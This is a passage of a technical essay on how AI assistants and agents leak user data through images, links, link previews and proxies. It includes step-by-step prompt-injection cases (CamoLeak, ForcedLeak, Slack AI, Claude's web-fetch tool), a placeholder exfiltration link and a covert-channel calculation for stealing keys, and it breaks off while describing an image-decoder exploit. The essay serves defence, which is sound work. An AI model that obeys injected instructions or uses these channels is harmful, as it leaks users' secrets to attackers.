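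GitLab's *CVE-2026-0540* (2026) traces the flaw to a search pattern that was meant to cover elements with special parsing rules but omitted five of them. DOMPurify works on a parsed tree, but this part was a string filter with an incomplete list, much like Copilot's link filter. DOMPurify 3.3.2 fixed the flaw.

The bypass is partly the application's fault, since it fails if the application inserts the sanitised HTML into an ordinary element. Sonar's *mXSS Explained* uses the term "desanitization" for when an application changes markup after the sanitiser has checked it, and warns that even small changes can undo the protection. A chat interface may make such changes for many reasons, for example to add source references or colour program code.

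Developers who write their own sanitisers probably do worse. In *Hand Sanitizers in the Wild*, Klein, Barber and colleagues (2022) studied custom JavaScript sanitisers on websites and automatically generated working exploits for 51.3% of the vulnerable ones. Most were too specialised to stop XSS in even a slightly different context.

A script in a chat window is worse than an image because it can send data out even under a strict CSP, as Janc pointed out.

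### Rejecting what a simple grammar does not recognise

Language-theoretic security is a school of thought that attributes such flaws to overly complex input formats. Its proponents advise developers to accept only input that matches a simple, fully specified grammar, and to parse that input once, before any other code acts on it.

Ali and Smith report that Sassaman and colleagues proposed a precise version of this advice, which is to restrict input formats to deterministic context-free languages. Roughly, a parser can read such a language from left to right, using a stack to track nested parts, without ever having to guess what comes next. A 1997 result shows that an algorithm can in principle decide whether two parsers for such languages accept exactly the same inputs. No algorithm can always decide this for context-free languages in general.

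The advice works well for formats in which some input is invalid. In 2022, a researcher found that Zoom's chat could deliver forged messages. Zoom's server and its app both accepted a byte sequence that UTF-8 forbids, but one read it as a single character and the other as three. An attacker could use this to make the app parse two messages where the server had parsed one. Either program could have prevented this by rejecting the invalid bytes.

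Every string is valid Markdown, so all CommonMark parsers accept the same inputs. They can still build different trees from the same string. To show that two parsers interpret Markdown the same way, a developer would have to prove that they build the same trees, not only that they accept the same inputs.

Reference-style links make that harder. `[menu][m]` is a link only if a definition with a matching label appears elsewhere in the document, possibly thousands of characters later. A context-free grammar cannot require two labels of any length to match, so Markdown falls outside the class of languages that Sassaman and colleagues recommend.

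A developer can still support a smaller notation, such as one with paragraphs, emphasis, lists and code but no reference-style links or raw HTML. A server can reject a malformed message, but users would not tolerate a chat service that withheld an answer because of a stray bracket. The renderer can instead display any unsupported syntax as literal characters. Every string can then be displayed, but only as text and a few harmless structures.

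The advice to parse once applies unchanged to Markdown. If the filter and the renderer use the same parse tree, they cannot interpret the answer differently.

### Three ways to build the filter

A developer can filter strings, filter a parsed tree, or build the display only from an allowlist of node types. Nodes are the parts of the tree, such as a paragraph, a link or emphasised text.

In the third design, the renderer parses the Markdown and goes through the tree node by node. For each node of a permitted type, it creates the matching element directly in the browser and inserts the text as text. For any other node, it displays the source characters. It never assembles an HTML string for the browser to parse. OSV recommends these direct browser calls instead of HTML strings.

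| Problem | Filtering strings | Filtering a parsed tree | Building from allowed node types |
|---|---|---|---|
| The model uses an unusual notation | The filter misses it unless it has a pattern for it | The filter finds it if its parser agrees with the renderer's | The notation does not matter, because the renderer checks the node type |
| The answer is still arriving | A late filter lets requests through | A late filter lets requests through | Each unfinished version contains only allowed node types |
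| The browser parses the HTML again | The meaning can change | The meaning can change if the filter writes the tree out as a string | There is no HTML string to parse |

String filters have the worst record, but they are easy to add to an existing product, which may be why they persist. Tree filters work considerably better if they use the browser's own parser. Klein and colleagues therefore recommend building a standard sanitiser into browsers. It should also pass on the tree itself rather than HTML, which the browser would have to parse again.

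Building the output from allowed node types would have stopped both attacks on Copilot, if the list excluded images and raw HTML. In Reddy and Gujral's table of defences, however, restricting the output to permitted Markdown fails to prevent a zero-click leak. The table is theoretical, since they did not reproduce the attack, and the safe subset they suggest elsewhere still includes plain images. An allowlist that includes images blocks only the unusual elements and still allows a leak by the route EchoLeak used.

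If a product needs images or links, the renderer also has to check their addresses. For links, this includes refusing addresses that begin with `javascript:`. For images, it means loading only from trusted servers, though an attacker can bypass this restriction through a trusted server that fetches other addresses.

A chat interface may pass code blocks to separate helper programs that highlight code or draw diagrams. Cursor's Mermaid leak began with a code block, a node type that almost any allowlist would permit. A helper therefore has to build its output from allowed node types too, or the renderer should show the code as text.

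## Restricting where images may load from

A vendor who wants to keep displaying images can load them only from an allowlist of servers, usually through the CSP directive `img-src`. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* points out that a product needs to contact comparatively few servers, so a developer can list them.

An allowlist restricts who receives a request, not what the request contains. Once a server is on the list, the model can write any data into the rest of the address. The vendor therefore relies on three premises about every permitted server:

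1. It belongs to the vendor or to a reputable company.
2. Nobody hostile can read what it records.
3. It does not pass requests on to other servers.

Researchers have found products in which each of these was false.

### An expired domain

Salesforce sells software for managing customers, and its Agentforce agents answer employees' questions about customer records. Some of these records come from strangers, because a feature called Web-to-Lead saves what visitors type into a form on a company's website as a "lead", or possible customer. In 2025, the security company Noma submitted instructions for the model through such a form, and they stayed in the saved lead until an employee asked Agentforce about it.

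Willison (2026) reproduces the instructions, which look like a short questionnaire. The questions are how many leads there are, what colour red and yellow make, and what email addresses the leads have. The last item is a request for a "preview image" with the email addresses in its URL.

Salesforce's CSP blocked images from unknown domains, but one permitted domain, which had Salesforce's name in it, had expired. In an attack it called ForcedLeak, Noma registered the domain for $5, according to BeyondMachines, and found the leads' data in its own server's log. Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed* adds that an attacker could also have taken details of planned sales and internal communications.

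The entry was presumably correct when Salesforce added it, but a CSP matches domain names, and the browser cannot detect when a domain has a new owner. Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025, and Nudge Security dates the fix to 8 September. Salesforce recovered the domain and, as The Hacker News (2025) reports, began enforcing an allowlist of URLs on its agents' output. This list covers links as well as images, but someone still has to keep it up to date.

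### A reputable host that stores data for strangers

Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant, had a CSP that allowed images from the Google Docs domain. Google is reputable, and outsiders cannot read its server logs. But Google Forms uses the same domain, and anyone can create a form there and read the responses.

A form's creator can write a link that already contains an answer, and opening the link submits it. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* shows how an attacker can use such a link as an image address:

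1. The attacker creates a form and emails the victim. The email tells the model that the user must be able to give feedback on search results, and supplies the form's address.
2. The user asks for a summary of recent mail. The assistant finds the attacker's email along with the others, even if the user has never opened it.
3. The model writes an image whose address is the form's submission link, with the text of the other emails filled in as the answer.
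4. The browser requests the "image", and Google stores the answer among the form's responses, where the attacker can read it.

A single answer leaked the full contents of several emails in one test and parts of more than 40 in another. PromptArmor reported this on the evening of Friday, 5 December 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on Monday and released its first fix on Tuesday.

Willison describes two similar failures in lists that control which servers an agent can contact, rather than where images can load from. By default, the browser tool in Google's Antigravity could visit a site where anyone can create an address and watch the requests it receives. Anthropic's Claude Cowork, an agent for office work, could contact Anthropic's own servers by default. PromptArmor's instructions contained an access key for the attacker's Anthropic account, and the agent uploaded the user's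 files to that account. Allowing a vendor's own domain is therefore unsafe if strangers can store data there.

### A host that passes requests on

OpenAI's `url_safe` check for ChatGPT always approved addresses at Bing. Bing's search results link to Bing addresses that redirect visitors to the listed sites. In Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025), researchers got their own sites into Bing's index and used the resulting Bing links as image addresses, and ChatGPT displayed the images.

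Tenable reported the flaw in December 2024, and it was still open when Tenable published the advisory. In July 2025, OpenAI told Tenable that it had improved the check, according to Tenable's later advisory, *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025).

A CSP would have stopped this redirect unless it also permitted the researchers' sites. After a redirect, the browser makes the second request itself and checks the new host against the policy. The browser cannot check the second address when the permitted server fetches it, as Teams did in EchoLeak and Bing's image search did in SearchLeak.

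PromptArmor raised the same concern with Notion, a note-taking service, and advised it to ensure that its image server could not be used to bypass its CSP. This is hard to guarantee for a server that someone else runs, because the vendor would have to know every function of every permitted host, including any the owner adds later.

### What a signed image proxy guarantees

An image proxy fetches remote images on the viewer's behalf, so the viewer's browser never contacts the original host. This hides the viewer's IP address, but the host still receives anything the model has written into the image's URL, because the proxy has to request that URL to get the image.

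GitHub's proxy, Camo, also requires image addresses to be signed, as Legit Security's *CamoLeak* explains. When someone saves a document with an external image, GitHub replaces the image's address with a Camo address that includes a signature, a code computed from the original address and a secret key. When a browser requests the image, Camo fetches it only if the signature is valid. Without the key, neither an attacker nor a model can compute a valid signature for a new address.

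The signature guarantees that GitHub has processed the image's address. GitHub processes addresses for anyone who saves a document or submits Markdown through its API, so a signature is not evidence that the image or its host is harmless.

Signed addresses prevent a model from adding data to them only if the signing happens before the model writes its answer. A chat service that signed the images in each answer just before displaying it would also sign any stolen data in their addresses. GitHub's Copilot Chat avoided this problem, since an image in an answer loaded only if its Camo address already had a valid signature.

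### CamoLeak

Copilot Chat answers developers' questions on GitHub and can read anything the user can read, including private repositories. In June 2025, Omer Mayraz of Legit Security got data out of it without forging a signature.

Mayraz first hid instructions for the model in the description of a pull request, a proposed change to a project's code, where GitHub lets authors include hidden comments. The project's owner received the usual notification, but the instructions did not appear in it or on the page. Copilot still read them, and when another user opened the pull request and asked for an explanation, it followed them with that user's permissions.

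Mayraz could now make Copilot fetch private code, encode it and attach it to a link, but the user had to click the link. An ordinary image did not work because GitHub's CSP blocked external hosts. He could load an image from his server only through Camo, and he could not sign an address that contained data he had not yet seen.

His solution was to prepare an alphabet:

1. He set up a server that answered every request with a transparent image one pixel wide.
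2. He chose an address on this server for each letter and symbol that might occur in the data, and had GitHub turn them all into signed Camo addresses.
3. He put the resulting dictionary into the hidden comment and asked Copilot to play a "small game", in which it wrote the private text as a row of images, using the matching image for each character.
4. The victim's browser requested the images from Camo, which checked the signatures and fetched them from Mayraz's server. He read the text from the order of the requests.

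Every request went to a permitted host and had a valid signature. The victim saw nothing unusual because the images in the row were transparent.

In his demonstration, Mayraz stole the description of an undisclosed vulnerability from a private project. He also had Copilot search the victim's code for "AWS_KEY", a common name for an access key to Amazon's cloud services, and leak what it found. Legit Security rates the flaw's severity at 9.6 out of 10. GitHub had fixed the flaw by 14 August. It did so by switching off images in Copilot Chat, although SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories* describes the fix only as disallowing the use of Camo for such leaks.

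### How much a choice can carry

CamoLeak worked because a choice among fixed addresses also carries information. Suppose an attacker has prepared N addresses and can see which one the renderer requests. One request distinguishes N possibilities, and k requests in a known order distinguish at most N<sup>k</sup>. In bits, this is

log₂(N<sup>k</sup>) = k × log₂ N,

so each request carries up to log₂ N bits.

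An access key of 40 characters, each drawn from 64 symbols, has 64⁴⁰ = 2²⁴⁰ possible values, or 240 bits. If the attacker has prepared one address per symbol, each request carries log₂ 64 = 6 bits, so stealing the key takes 240 / 6 = 40 requests. A single address with 2,000 characters of data carries as much as 2,000 of these requests. Preventing the model from writing its own addresses therefore makes stealing a whole document much slower, but barely protects a password.

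Reducing the number of addresses gives limited protection. An attacker with only two addresses can still extract the same key in 240 requests, compared with 20 requests with 4,096 addresses, one for each pair of symbols. Capping the number of requests is more effective, since five requests among 64 addresses carry only 30 bits, or five characters of the key. But even one request to one of two addresses can reveal whether the user's inbox mentions a merger.

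Choosing among harmless addresses is a covert channel, a way to send information through something not designed to carry it. dyb's *The Read-Only Lie* traces the idea to a 1973 paper by Butler Lampson and points out that the timing, order and number of requests can carry information too. The log₂ N limit covers only the model's choice of address.

### Caching and batching

The limit assumes that every choice reaches the attacker. Browsers and proxies often cache images instead of fetching them again, so if the leaked word is "coffee", the attacker's server may receive only one f and one e. Requests can also arrive out of order.

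Mayraz avoided the cache by telling Copilot to add a new random number to the end of each Camo address. Camo evidently accepted the altered addresses, so its signature cannot have covered the added number. A proxy that rejected any change to a signed address would have made CamoLeak harder to carry out.

Loading each address at most once does not stop an attacker from leaking text through image requests. Radware's *ZombieAgent*, an attack on ChatGPT, used a separate set of addresses for each position in the text. Addresses for the first position might end in a0, b0 or c0, and those for the second in a1, b1 or c1. No address has to be used twice, and the attacker can reconstruct the text regardless of the order in which the requests arrive. Leaking a 40-character key drawn from 64 symbols this way takes 40 × 64 = 2,560 addresses but only 40 requests.

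If caching means the server receives at most one request for each of N addresses, and the order of requests is unreliable, the attacker learns only which addresses were requested. There are 2<sup>N</sup> possible combinations, so N addresses carry at most N bits. A 240-bit key needs at least 240 addresses, one per bit. The model requests those whose bit is 1, which is about 120 requests for a random key. Caching makes the attacker prepare more addresses, but a script can do that in seconds.

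An attacker who prepares an address for each pair or triple of characters needs fewer requests. A proxy can fetch all the images in an answer together and in random order, which defeats Mayraz's version of the attack but not a version that numbers the characters' positions.

To hide the choice, the proxy would have to fetch every image when it signs the address, store a copy, and never contact the original host again. The attacker's server would then receive the same requests whatever the model later wrote. The proxy would need more storage, and images that are supposed to change, such as a badge showing whether a program's latest tests passed, would go out of date.

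### OpenAI's rule for public addresses

OpenAI also tried to stop models from composing addresses. By September 2025, ChatGPT could open an address only if it left the address unchanged, and it refused to add parameters even when told to. Radware's attack got past this with an email that listed a prepared address for each letter, each digit, and the space. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something with Gmail, it read the email, looked for sensitive information, and opened the addresses that spelled out what it found.

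Most of these requests came from OpenAI's servers rather than the user's browser, so a CSP in the chat window would not have affected them. Radware reported the flaw on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, after the fix ChatGPT would open a link from an email only if the link was in a well-known public index or the user had supplied it.

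On 28 January 2026, OpenAI explained its wider rule in OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026). It rejects lists of trusted sites for two reasons. Many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere, and a strict list causes so many false alarms that people learn to click through the warnings. OpenAI instead checks the exact address:

1. A crawler, a program that explores the web as a search engine does, records the public addresses it finds. It has no access to users' conversations or accounts.
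2. Before an agent loads a page or an image automatically, the system looks for the complete address in the crawler's records.
3. If it finds the address, the agent may load it. Otherwise the agent has to try another site, or the user sees a warning that the link may contain information from the conversation.

If the model adds a password to a URL, the crawler is very unlikely to have seen the resulting URL. The rule doesn't depend on whether a site is reputable, so it would also cover Google Forms.

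OpenAI claims only to prevent agents from "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself". It does not promise that a page is truthful or free of hostile instructions. Nor does the guarantee cover leaks in which no single address contains private data, such as Rehberger's method, which uses one address per letter. Once the crawler has recorded the attacker's pages, every address is public, but the model's choice among them can still reveal what the user has told it.

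OpenAI's accompanying paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, acknowledges this bypass, according to Embrace The Red. Rehberger adds that anyone with a larger website probably already has 36 indexed pages, one for each letter and digit, and that an attacker could teach the model a vocabulary of thousands. He suggests that OpenAI cache each response for a few minutes or prevent an agent from visiting the same address twice in a session, though he had not tested whether OpenAI already did so. Either measure would stop repeated use of the 36 pages, but an attacker with a few thousand indexed pages could number the positions, as Radware did.

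Rehberger also warned that OpenAI's developers might not apply the rule everywhere. In April 2026, PromptArmor used the Google Forms method against Codex, OpenAI's agent, which had recently gained plugins for email and other everyday work. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* reports that asking Codex to review the inbox was enough to leak the full contents of other emails. No crawler could have seen a form link containing those emails, so Codex evidently did not apply the rule to its images. OpenAI has since fixed the flaw.

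### Claude's web-fetch tool

Anthropic used a different rule for its web-fetch tool, which lets Claude read web pages. When Anthropic released the tool to developers in September 2025, Claude could not construct addresses and could open only those that had already appeared in the conversation, including in the results of earlier searches and fetches. Anthropic warned that some risk of leaks remained.

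In July 2026, Ayush Paul showed how to exploit the addresses in fetched pages (Willison, 2026). He built a site that showed Claude a fake security check. In it, he claimed that AI assistants had to identify their user, and that the tool's limitations meant Claude would have to find the user's profile letter by letter. The page linked to a separate address for each possible first letter, each of those pages linked to addresses for the second letter, and so on.

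Claude had stored information about the user from earlier conversations, and it followed the links that spelled out their name, home city and employer. The site showed the fake check only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a user who opened the site in a browser to see whether it was safe would not have found the instructions.

According to dyb, each page offered 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen. Each choice of link therefore carried log₂ 27 ≈ 4.75 bits, so about 30 choices carried about 143 bits.

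Each address contained all the letters chosen so far and was new, so neither caching nor a ban on repeat visits would have stopped this attack. Paul's server could create each set of links when Claude arrived, so he did not have to prepare the pages in advance. OpenAI's rule makes this much harder, because a crawler would have to record 27⁶, or about 387 million, pages to cover every six-letter name. The attacker would have to return to a smaller set of numbered addresses.

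Tencent's *Why AI Agent’s Memory Becomes Attacker’s Data Goldmine* (2026) reproduced the attack with 37 symbols and stole an access key. Its agent took one to two seconds per character, so a 40-character key would take about a minute. The test is weak evidence of how often a commercial product would comply, because Tencent had told its agent to follow instructions on web pages and complete verification steps.

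Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the flaw internally and did not pay him a reward. Anthropic fixed the flaw by preventing the tool from following links in pages it has fetched. Claude can still open addresses that the user enters or that its search tool returns. An attacker would now have to get a suitable set of pages into the search results or prepared addresses into the user's message. Willison had warned about the second route in 2025, because many applications insert emails or documents into what the model receives as the user's message.

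### What the rules stop and what they cost

| Rule | Can the model add data to an address? | Can it leak data by choosing? | What users lose |
|---|---|---|---|
| Allowlist of hosts | Yes | Yes, if any of the three premises is false | Pictures from other hosts |
| Proxy with addresses signed in advance | No, if the signature covers the whole address | Yes | Pictures without an existing signature |
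| Only addresses the model has already received | No | Yes | Pages whose address the model has to work out |
| Only addresses in an independent index | No | Yes, among indexed pages | Automatic loading of new, private or personalised pages |
| Only addresses from the user or a search | No | Yes, but only among those addresses | Links from one page to the next |
| Only copies stored before the model starts | No | No | New pictures and pictures that change |

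Users lose little when a chat window shows only stored copies of images, because most answers make sense without a new image from an unknown server. They lose only slightly more when images are turned off entirely.

The choice is harder for an agent that browses the web, because it must follow links to work through documentation that spans several pages. dyb proposes allowing links only on domains that the user has named in the conversation. But Paul's site looked like an ordinary coffee shop's to anyone who opened it in a browser, so a user who asked Claude about the shop would have approved the attacker's domain.

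Willison (2026) reports that OpenAI is making Lockdown Mode, an optional setting that limits outbound requests that could carry sensitive data, available to eligible personal accounts, including free ones. Users who leave it off keep the convenience of automatic loading, but their data could still leak through public addresses.

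## Link previews and clicks

A chat window that loads no images can still leak data if the model's text ends up in a messaging app. Many people now use AI agents through apps such as Slack, Microsoft Teams or Telegram. These apps often visit each link in a message to show a link preview with a title and picture, a process called unfurling.

Suppose an agent posts this message:

`Lunch is here: PAGE?q=DATA`

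PAGE is on the attacker's server, and DATA is text from the user's files. The preview takes four steps:

1. The app looks for web addresses in the message.
2. It, or a server working for it, requests the complete address, including DATA.
3. It reads the title, description and picture address from the page's metadata.
4. It fetches the picture and displays the preview below the message.

The attacker has the data after the second step, even if the page is empty and no preview ever appears.

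### Who makes the request

Mysk's *Link Previews* (2020), a study of popular chat apps on iOS and Android, found that the request for a link preview could come from three places. The linked site receives the full URL in each case, but the information it gets about the users depends on where the request comes from.

| Where the app fetches the page | Whose IP address the site sees | Who else learns the link | Apps in 2020 |
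|---|---|---|---|
| Sender's device | The sender's | Nobody, if the chat is end-to-end encrypted | iMessage, Signal, Viber, WhatsApp |
| Recipient's device | The recipient's | Nobody, if the chat is end-to-end encrypted | Two apps that Mysk did not name |
| App's server | Normally only the server's | The company that runs the app | Discord, Slack, Zoom, LinkedIn, Instagram and others |

If the recipient's device fetches the preview, a stranger can find out roughly where someone is by sending them a link. Fetching it from a server avoids this, but the company running the server receives the link and at least part of the page. Slack's servers downloaded up to 50 MB per link, and Slack told Mysk that it kept previews for about 30 minutes. LINE, an end-to-end encrypted app, sent links from decrypted messages to its own server. Until LINE fixed the leak, that server also passed both users' IP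 addresses to the linked site.

Preview servers are also renderers, and some run scripts from the pages they visit. In Mysk's test, Instagram's and LinkedIn's servers did so for at least 20 seconds.

A CSP in the reader's browser cannot stop a server from fetching a link, because the browser never contacts the linked site. The server may fetch the link before anyone reads the message. When Mysk sent a link to a file through Instagram, several Facebook servers immediately began downloading the file.

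### Why previews were tolerable before

Mysk considered the sender's device the safest place to build a preview, assuming that people trust the links they send. Previews of such links also rarely leak anything to the linked site, because people usually copy a link from a page they have opened, and the preview only repeats a request the site has already received for the same address. The main privacy risk was that someone else would see the link or the page, for example when a server copied a private document.

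A model can write an address that nobody has ever requested and put private data in it. The preview request then delivers the data to the server at that address. Fetching the preview from the sender's device no longer helps, because the sender is the agent.

Restricting which sites get previews would help more. Signal's *I link therefore I am* announced link previews that at first covered only Imgur, Instagram, Reddit and YouTube. Such an allowlist depends on the same assumptions as an allowlist for images.

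### Links posted by agents

In Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks and what to do about it* (2024), Rehberger posted a link to his own server in Slack through a webhook, an address that lets a program send messages to Slack. His server's log recorded a visit from "Slackbot-LinkExpanding". A chatbot that posts its answers this way can therefore leak a conversation if a hostile website it reads gets it to put the conversation's text in a link. Willison (2024), in a post with the same title, notes that Discord fetches links too.

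Anthropic's Slack server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting models to other software, also did not turn off link previews when it posted messages. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* describes an attack on a developer who asked Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, to analyse a source file. Invisible instructions in the file made the agent read the project's `.env` file and post a link containing its secrets to Slack. Slack leaked the secrets when it previewed the link, so securing Claude Code's own display would not have helped.

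VulnCheck's *Anthropic Slack MCP Server Data Exfiltration via Link Unfurling* rates the flaw 9.3 out of 10 and lists all default deployments as affected. The server was already deprecated, according to the National Vulnerability Database's *CVE-2025-34072 Detail*, but developers may still be running copies of it.

### PromptArmor's tests

In February 2026, PromptArmor invited the public to test combinations of agents and messaging apps (*Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*). Participants had their agent write a link to a test site, AITextRisk.com, which logged any preview request and the data in it. They could then "claim" the log entry and report which agent produced it. They could also report agents whose links didn't trigger a request.

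PromptArmor found that OpenClaw, an agent operated through messaging apps, leaked data through Telegram in its default configuration. Apostol's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* also lists Microsoft's Copilot Studio in Teams and certain bots in Slack as affected. SoftwareSeni's *The agentic browser attack surface you are not thinking about*, a second-hand account, adds OpenClaw in Discord and Cursor's bot in Slack, and describes the Claude app in Slack as safer.

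If that account is right, two agents in the same app gave different results. An agent's developer can tell Slack not to fetch links, which may explain the difference, though the published results do not show the cause.

The positive results are stronger evidence than the negative ones, because a logged request with data in it shows that something fetched the link. A missing request could also mean that the agent changed the link or that an administrator had turned previews off. The number of requests is a poor measure of how dangerous a combination is. Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio produced the largest share, which SoftwareSeni attributes to how many companies use it. Because participants were testing their own agents, the results do not show how often an agent would obey a stranger's instructions.

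### Turning previews off

A developer can turn off Slack's previews for a message by setting both `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false. The first covers pages that are mainly text, and the second covers images, video and audio. Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* explains that Slack's servers have to fetch every URL to find out which kind it is, so setting only one option to false presumably hides some previews without preventing the request.

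For the same reason, the linked server's log is a better test of the preview setting than what appears in the chat. Slack's documentation states that Slack previews all links by default, but in one of its examples, a link to a text page gets no preview unless the developer asks for one. Slack may still have fetched that page to classify it.

Slack's *Share links and set preview preferences* explains how readers can hide link previews or remove one from a message. Doing so changes what the reader sees, but Slack's server has probably contacted the linked site by then.

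OpenClaw's users can turn off Telegram previews by setting `linkPreview: false` in a configuration file. PromptArmor recommended this in its report, but OpenClaw's *Telegram* documentation for version 2026.6.9 still lists previews as on by default. By default, OpenClaw also posts a partial reply and edits it as the model writes. A filter for dangerous links would have to run before OpenClaw posts that first version, as it would in a chat window that displays unfinished answers.

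Slack's documentation now advises developers to consider disabling previews for messages from a language model, but developers still have to disable them themselves. PromptArmor wants messaging apps to offer preview settings for each channel so that an administrator could set up a channel that is safe for agents.

The model should not be able to change the link preview setting, wherever it is stored. If an agent composes its own requests to Slack, an attacker can instruct it to leave out the two options that disable previews. An agent that can edit its own configuration file could turn previews back on. The program that sends the messages should add the options after the model has finished writing, or the messaging app should enforce the setting itself.

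### Security scanners

Security tools for email and chat may also open links to check them for malware or phishing, which can leak data in the same way as a preview. A scanner that requests the complete address sends any data in it before checking the page, so blocking the link afterwards does not prevent the leak. If opening the link submits an answer to an online form, as in the attack on Superhuman, the scanner may submit that answer.

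Turning off previews does not stop a separate scanner from visiting links. The scanner could avoid the visit by checking the host name against a list of known malicious sites, but a newly registered domain would not be on the list. It could also remove the parameters from the address before visiting, but attackers can put data in other parts of the address, and some pages do not work without their parameters.

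A scanner may also receive a link only after the user taps it. In 2020, when a user tapped a link in Viber, the app sent it to Viber's servers for fraud protection and personalised ads, according to Mysk. The servers received the address even though Viber's chats were end-to-end encrypted.

A company can test whether anything opens its links automatically by sending itself a unique, harmless link to a server it controls. Any request that arrives before someone clicks must come from a preview, a scanner or another automatic process.

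### The Slack AI leak

If nothing visits a link automatically, the attacker needs the user to click it. Slack AI, a feature that answers questions about a company's Slack messages, could be made to write such a link in August 2024. PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* describes the attack:

1. A user stores an API key, a password for software, in a private channel.
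2. An attacker with an account in the same Slack workspace creates a public channel and posts instructions there. No one else has to join the channel, because Slack AI also searches public channels that the user has not joined.
3. The user asks Slack AI for the key. Slack AI retrieves both messages and gives them to the model.
4. The model follows the attacker's instructions. It displays an error message with a link labelled "click here to reauthenticate" and puts the key in the link's address.
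5. The user clicks, and the browser sends the key to the attacker's server.

The attacker never had access to the private channel and did not need to know the key. The answer cited only the user's own message, so it looked as if nothing else had influenced it. The attacker's message did not appear on the first page of search results either. In a second test, which used the same method to show a phishing link, Slack AI did cite the attacker's channel.

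Slack AI also began to draw on uploaded files on 14 August, the day PromptArmor reported the flaw. PromptArmor had finished its tests before the change, but thought it highly likely that instructions in a document would work too. In that case, the attacker would no longer need a Slack account.

Slack replied on 19 August that the evidence was insufficient and that all members of a workspace could search public channels by design. The reply did not address the leak, because the stolen key was in a private channel. Willison (2024), in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection*, concluded from the reply that Slack did not yet understand the problem. Slack later patched the flaw, according to the AI-generated summary in the OECD's *Slack AI Vulnerability Exposes Private Channel Data* (2024).

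### Warnings and visible addresses

Users could have seen where the link in the Slack AI answer led by holding the mouse pointer over it. When PromptArmor did this, the attacker's address appeared with the key in it. But users had to think to check, and the error message gave them an ordinary reason to click.

Showing the full address next to every link would remove that step, but people would still have to recognise the data in the address. In base64url, for example, "lunch at noon" becomes `bHVuY2ggYXQgbm9vbg`, which looks much like the codes in many legitimate addresses. If the model leaks data by choosing among prepared addresses, the address contains nothing to recognise.

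ChatGPT asks users to approve some links before it opens them. OpenAI's *ChatGPT generated links* explains that the decision depends partly on what OpenAI has found by scanning websites. OpenAI's rule for public addresses uses the same approach. ChatGPT asks for approval of every link to a site whose owner has told OpenAI not to catalogue it. According to Gend's *AI agent link safety*, the dialog warns that the link is not verified and may include information from the conversation, and lets the user copy the link or open it anyway.

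A dialog like this at least makes the possible leak visible, but the user still has to judge it. OpenAI gives the example of a search for cars, where the link tells the car site that the user lives in London. Most people would accept that, but a harmful link can have the same form. OpenAI advises users to check which website the link leads to and whether they trust it. That would probably help with an unknown domain, but less with an attacker's Google form.

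OpenAI does not report how often people stop at the dialog, so its benefit is hard to estimate, but it may be small. If the warning appears often, people may learn to click through it, which was OpenAI's own objection to strict lists of trusted sites. In the attack by Odson and Morris, the user approved a request that hid the address. A more useful dialog would name the site and show the data it would receive, decoded where possible.

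Displaying model-written links as plain text prevents accidental clicks and gives users time to look at the address. It is somewhat less convenient, since users have to copy each address they want to visit. It also works only if no later program turns the text into a link or fetches the address. Rehberger's Slack message contained a web address without link markup, and Slack still fetched it.

Copying a link is not always safe either. When a user pastes a suspicious address into Slack to ask a colleague about it, Slack's server fetches the page for a preview. If an app installed in the workspace has registered the address's domain with Slack, the app can receive the address as soon as the user pastes it, before they send the message. Slack previews only complete addresses, so the user can avoid this by leaving out the `https://`.

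## Exploits against image decoders and font engines

In the leaks described so far, the renderer worked as intended when it fetched an address or displayed a link. A file can also exploit a bug in the renderer to run an attacker's code. The bug is usually in a decoder, which turns a compressed image into pixels, or in a font engine, which turns characters into shapes.

### How a file can run code

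A decoder first reads numbers such as the image's width and height from the file. It uses them to reserve a buffer, a block of memory for the pixels, and then fills it. Most older decoders are written in C or C++, where a program does not check that each write stays inside the buffer unless the programmer adds a check. If the file's numbers make the buffer too small and the check is missing, the decoder overwrites whatever comes next in memory.

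An integer overflow can occur when a decoder adds up how many letter shapes a file contains. If the decoder stores the total as a 32-bit number, the count starts again at 0 after 4,294,967,295. When the file's tables add up to 4,294,967,300 shapes, the decoder stores a total of 4, reserves room for four shapes, and then starts to write more than four billion.

When a decoder writes past the end of a buffer, the program often crashes. But programs keep the addresses of their own functions in memory, and if the decoder overwrites one, the program may later jump to an address the attacker chose. Attackers therefore try to control what lies next to the buffer by including data that makes the decoder reserve and release memory in a planned order. Operating systems make this harder by loading code at random addresses, and recent iPhones also check a cryptographic signature on many stored addresses.

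Messaging apps may decode an image before anyone opens the message. Groß (2020), of Google's security research team Project Zero, found several flaws in image parsers that an attacker could reach this way on Apple devices. The flaws were in libraries that the messaging apps used, not in the apps' own code.

### Three attacks through images

Citizen Lab (2021), a research group at the University of Toronto, found such an attack on a Saudi activist's phone. It named the attack FORCEDENTRY and attributed it to NSO Group, which sells spyware to governments. NSO had probably used it since February 2021. Apple fixed the flaw on 13 September.

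The attack began with an iMessage attachment whose name ended in `.gif`. Apple wanted GIFs to loop endlessly, so iMessage processed each one before displaying it. Beer and Groß (2021) explain that Apple's image library, ImageIO, ignored the file's name and guessed the format from its contents. This exposed more than 20 decoders to anyone who could send a message. The "GIF" was a PDF containing an image in JBIG2, a format from the 1990s for compressing scanned text.

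JBIG2 saves space by storing one copy of each letter shape and a list of places to draw it. The decoder kept its count of the shapes in a 32-bit integer, which overflowed as in the example above. The resulting writes changed the recorded height of the page, so later drawing commands could read and write memory far outside the page.

The attackers still had to calculate where to write, and JBIG2 has no scripting language. It does have commands that correct a letter by combining bits with the logical operations AND, OR, XOR and XNOR. These are enough to build a NAND gate:

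A NAND B = (A AND B) XOR 1

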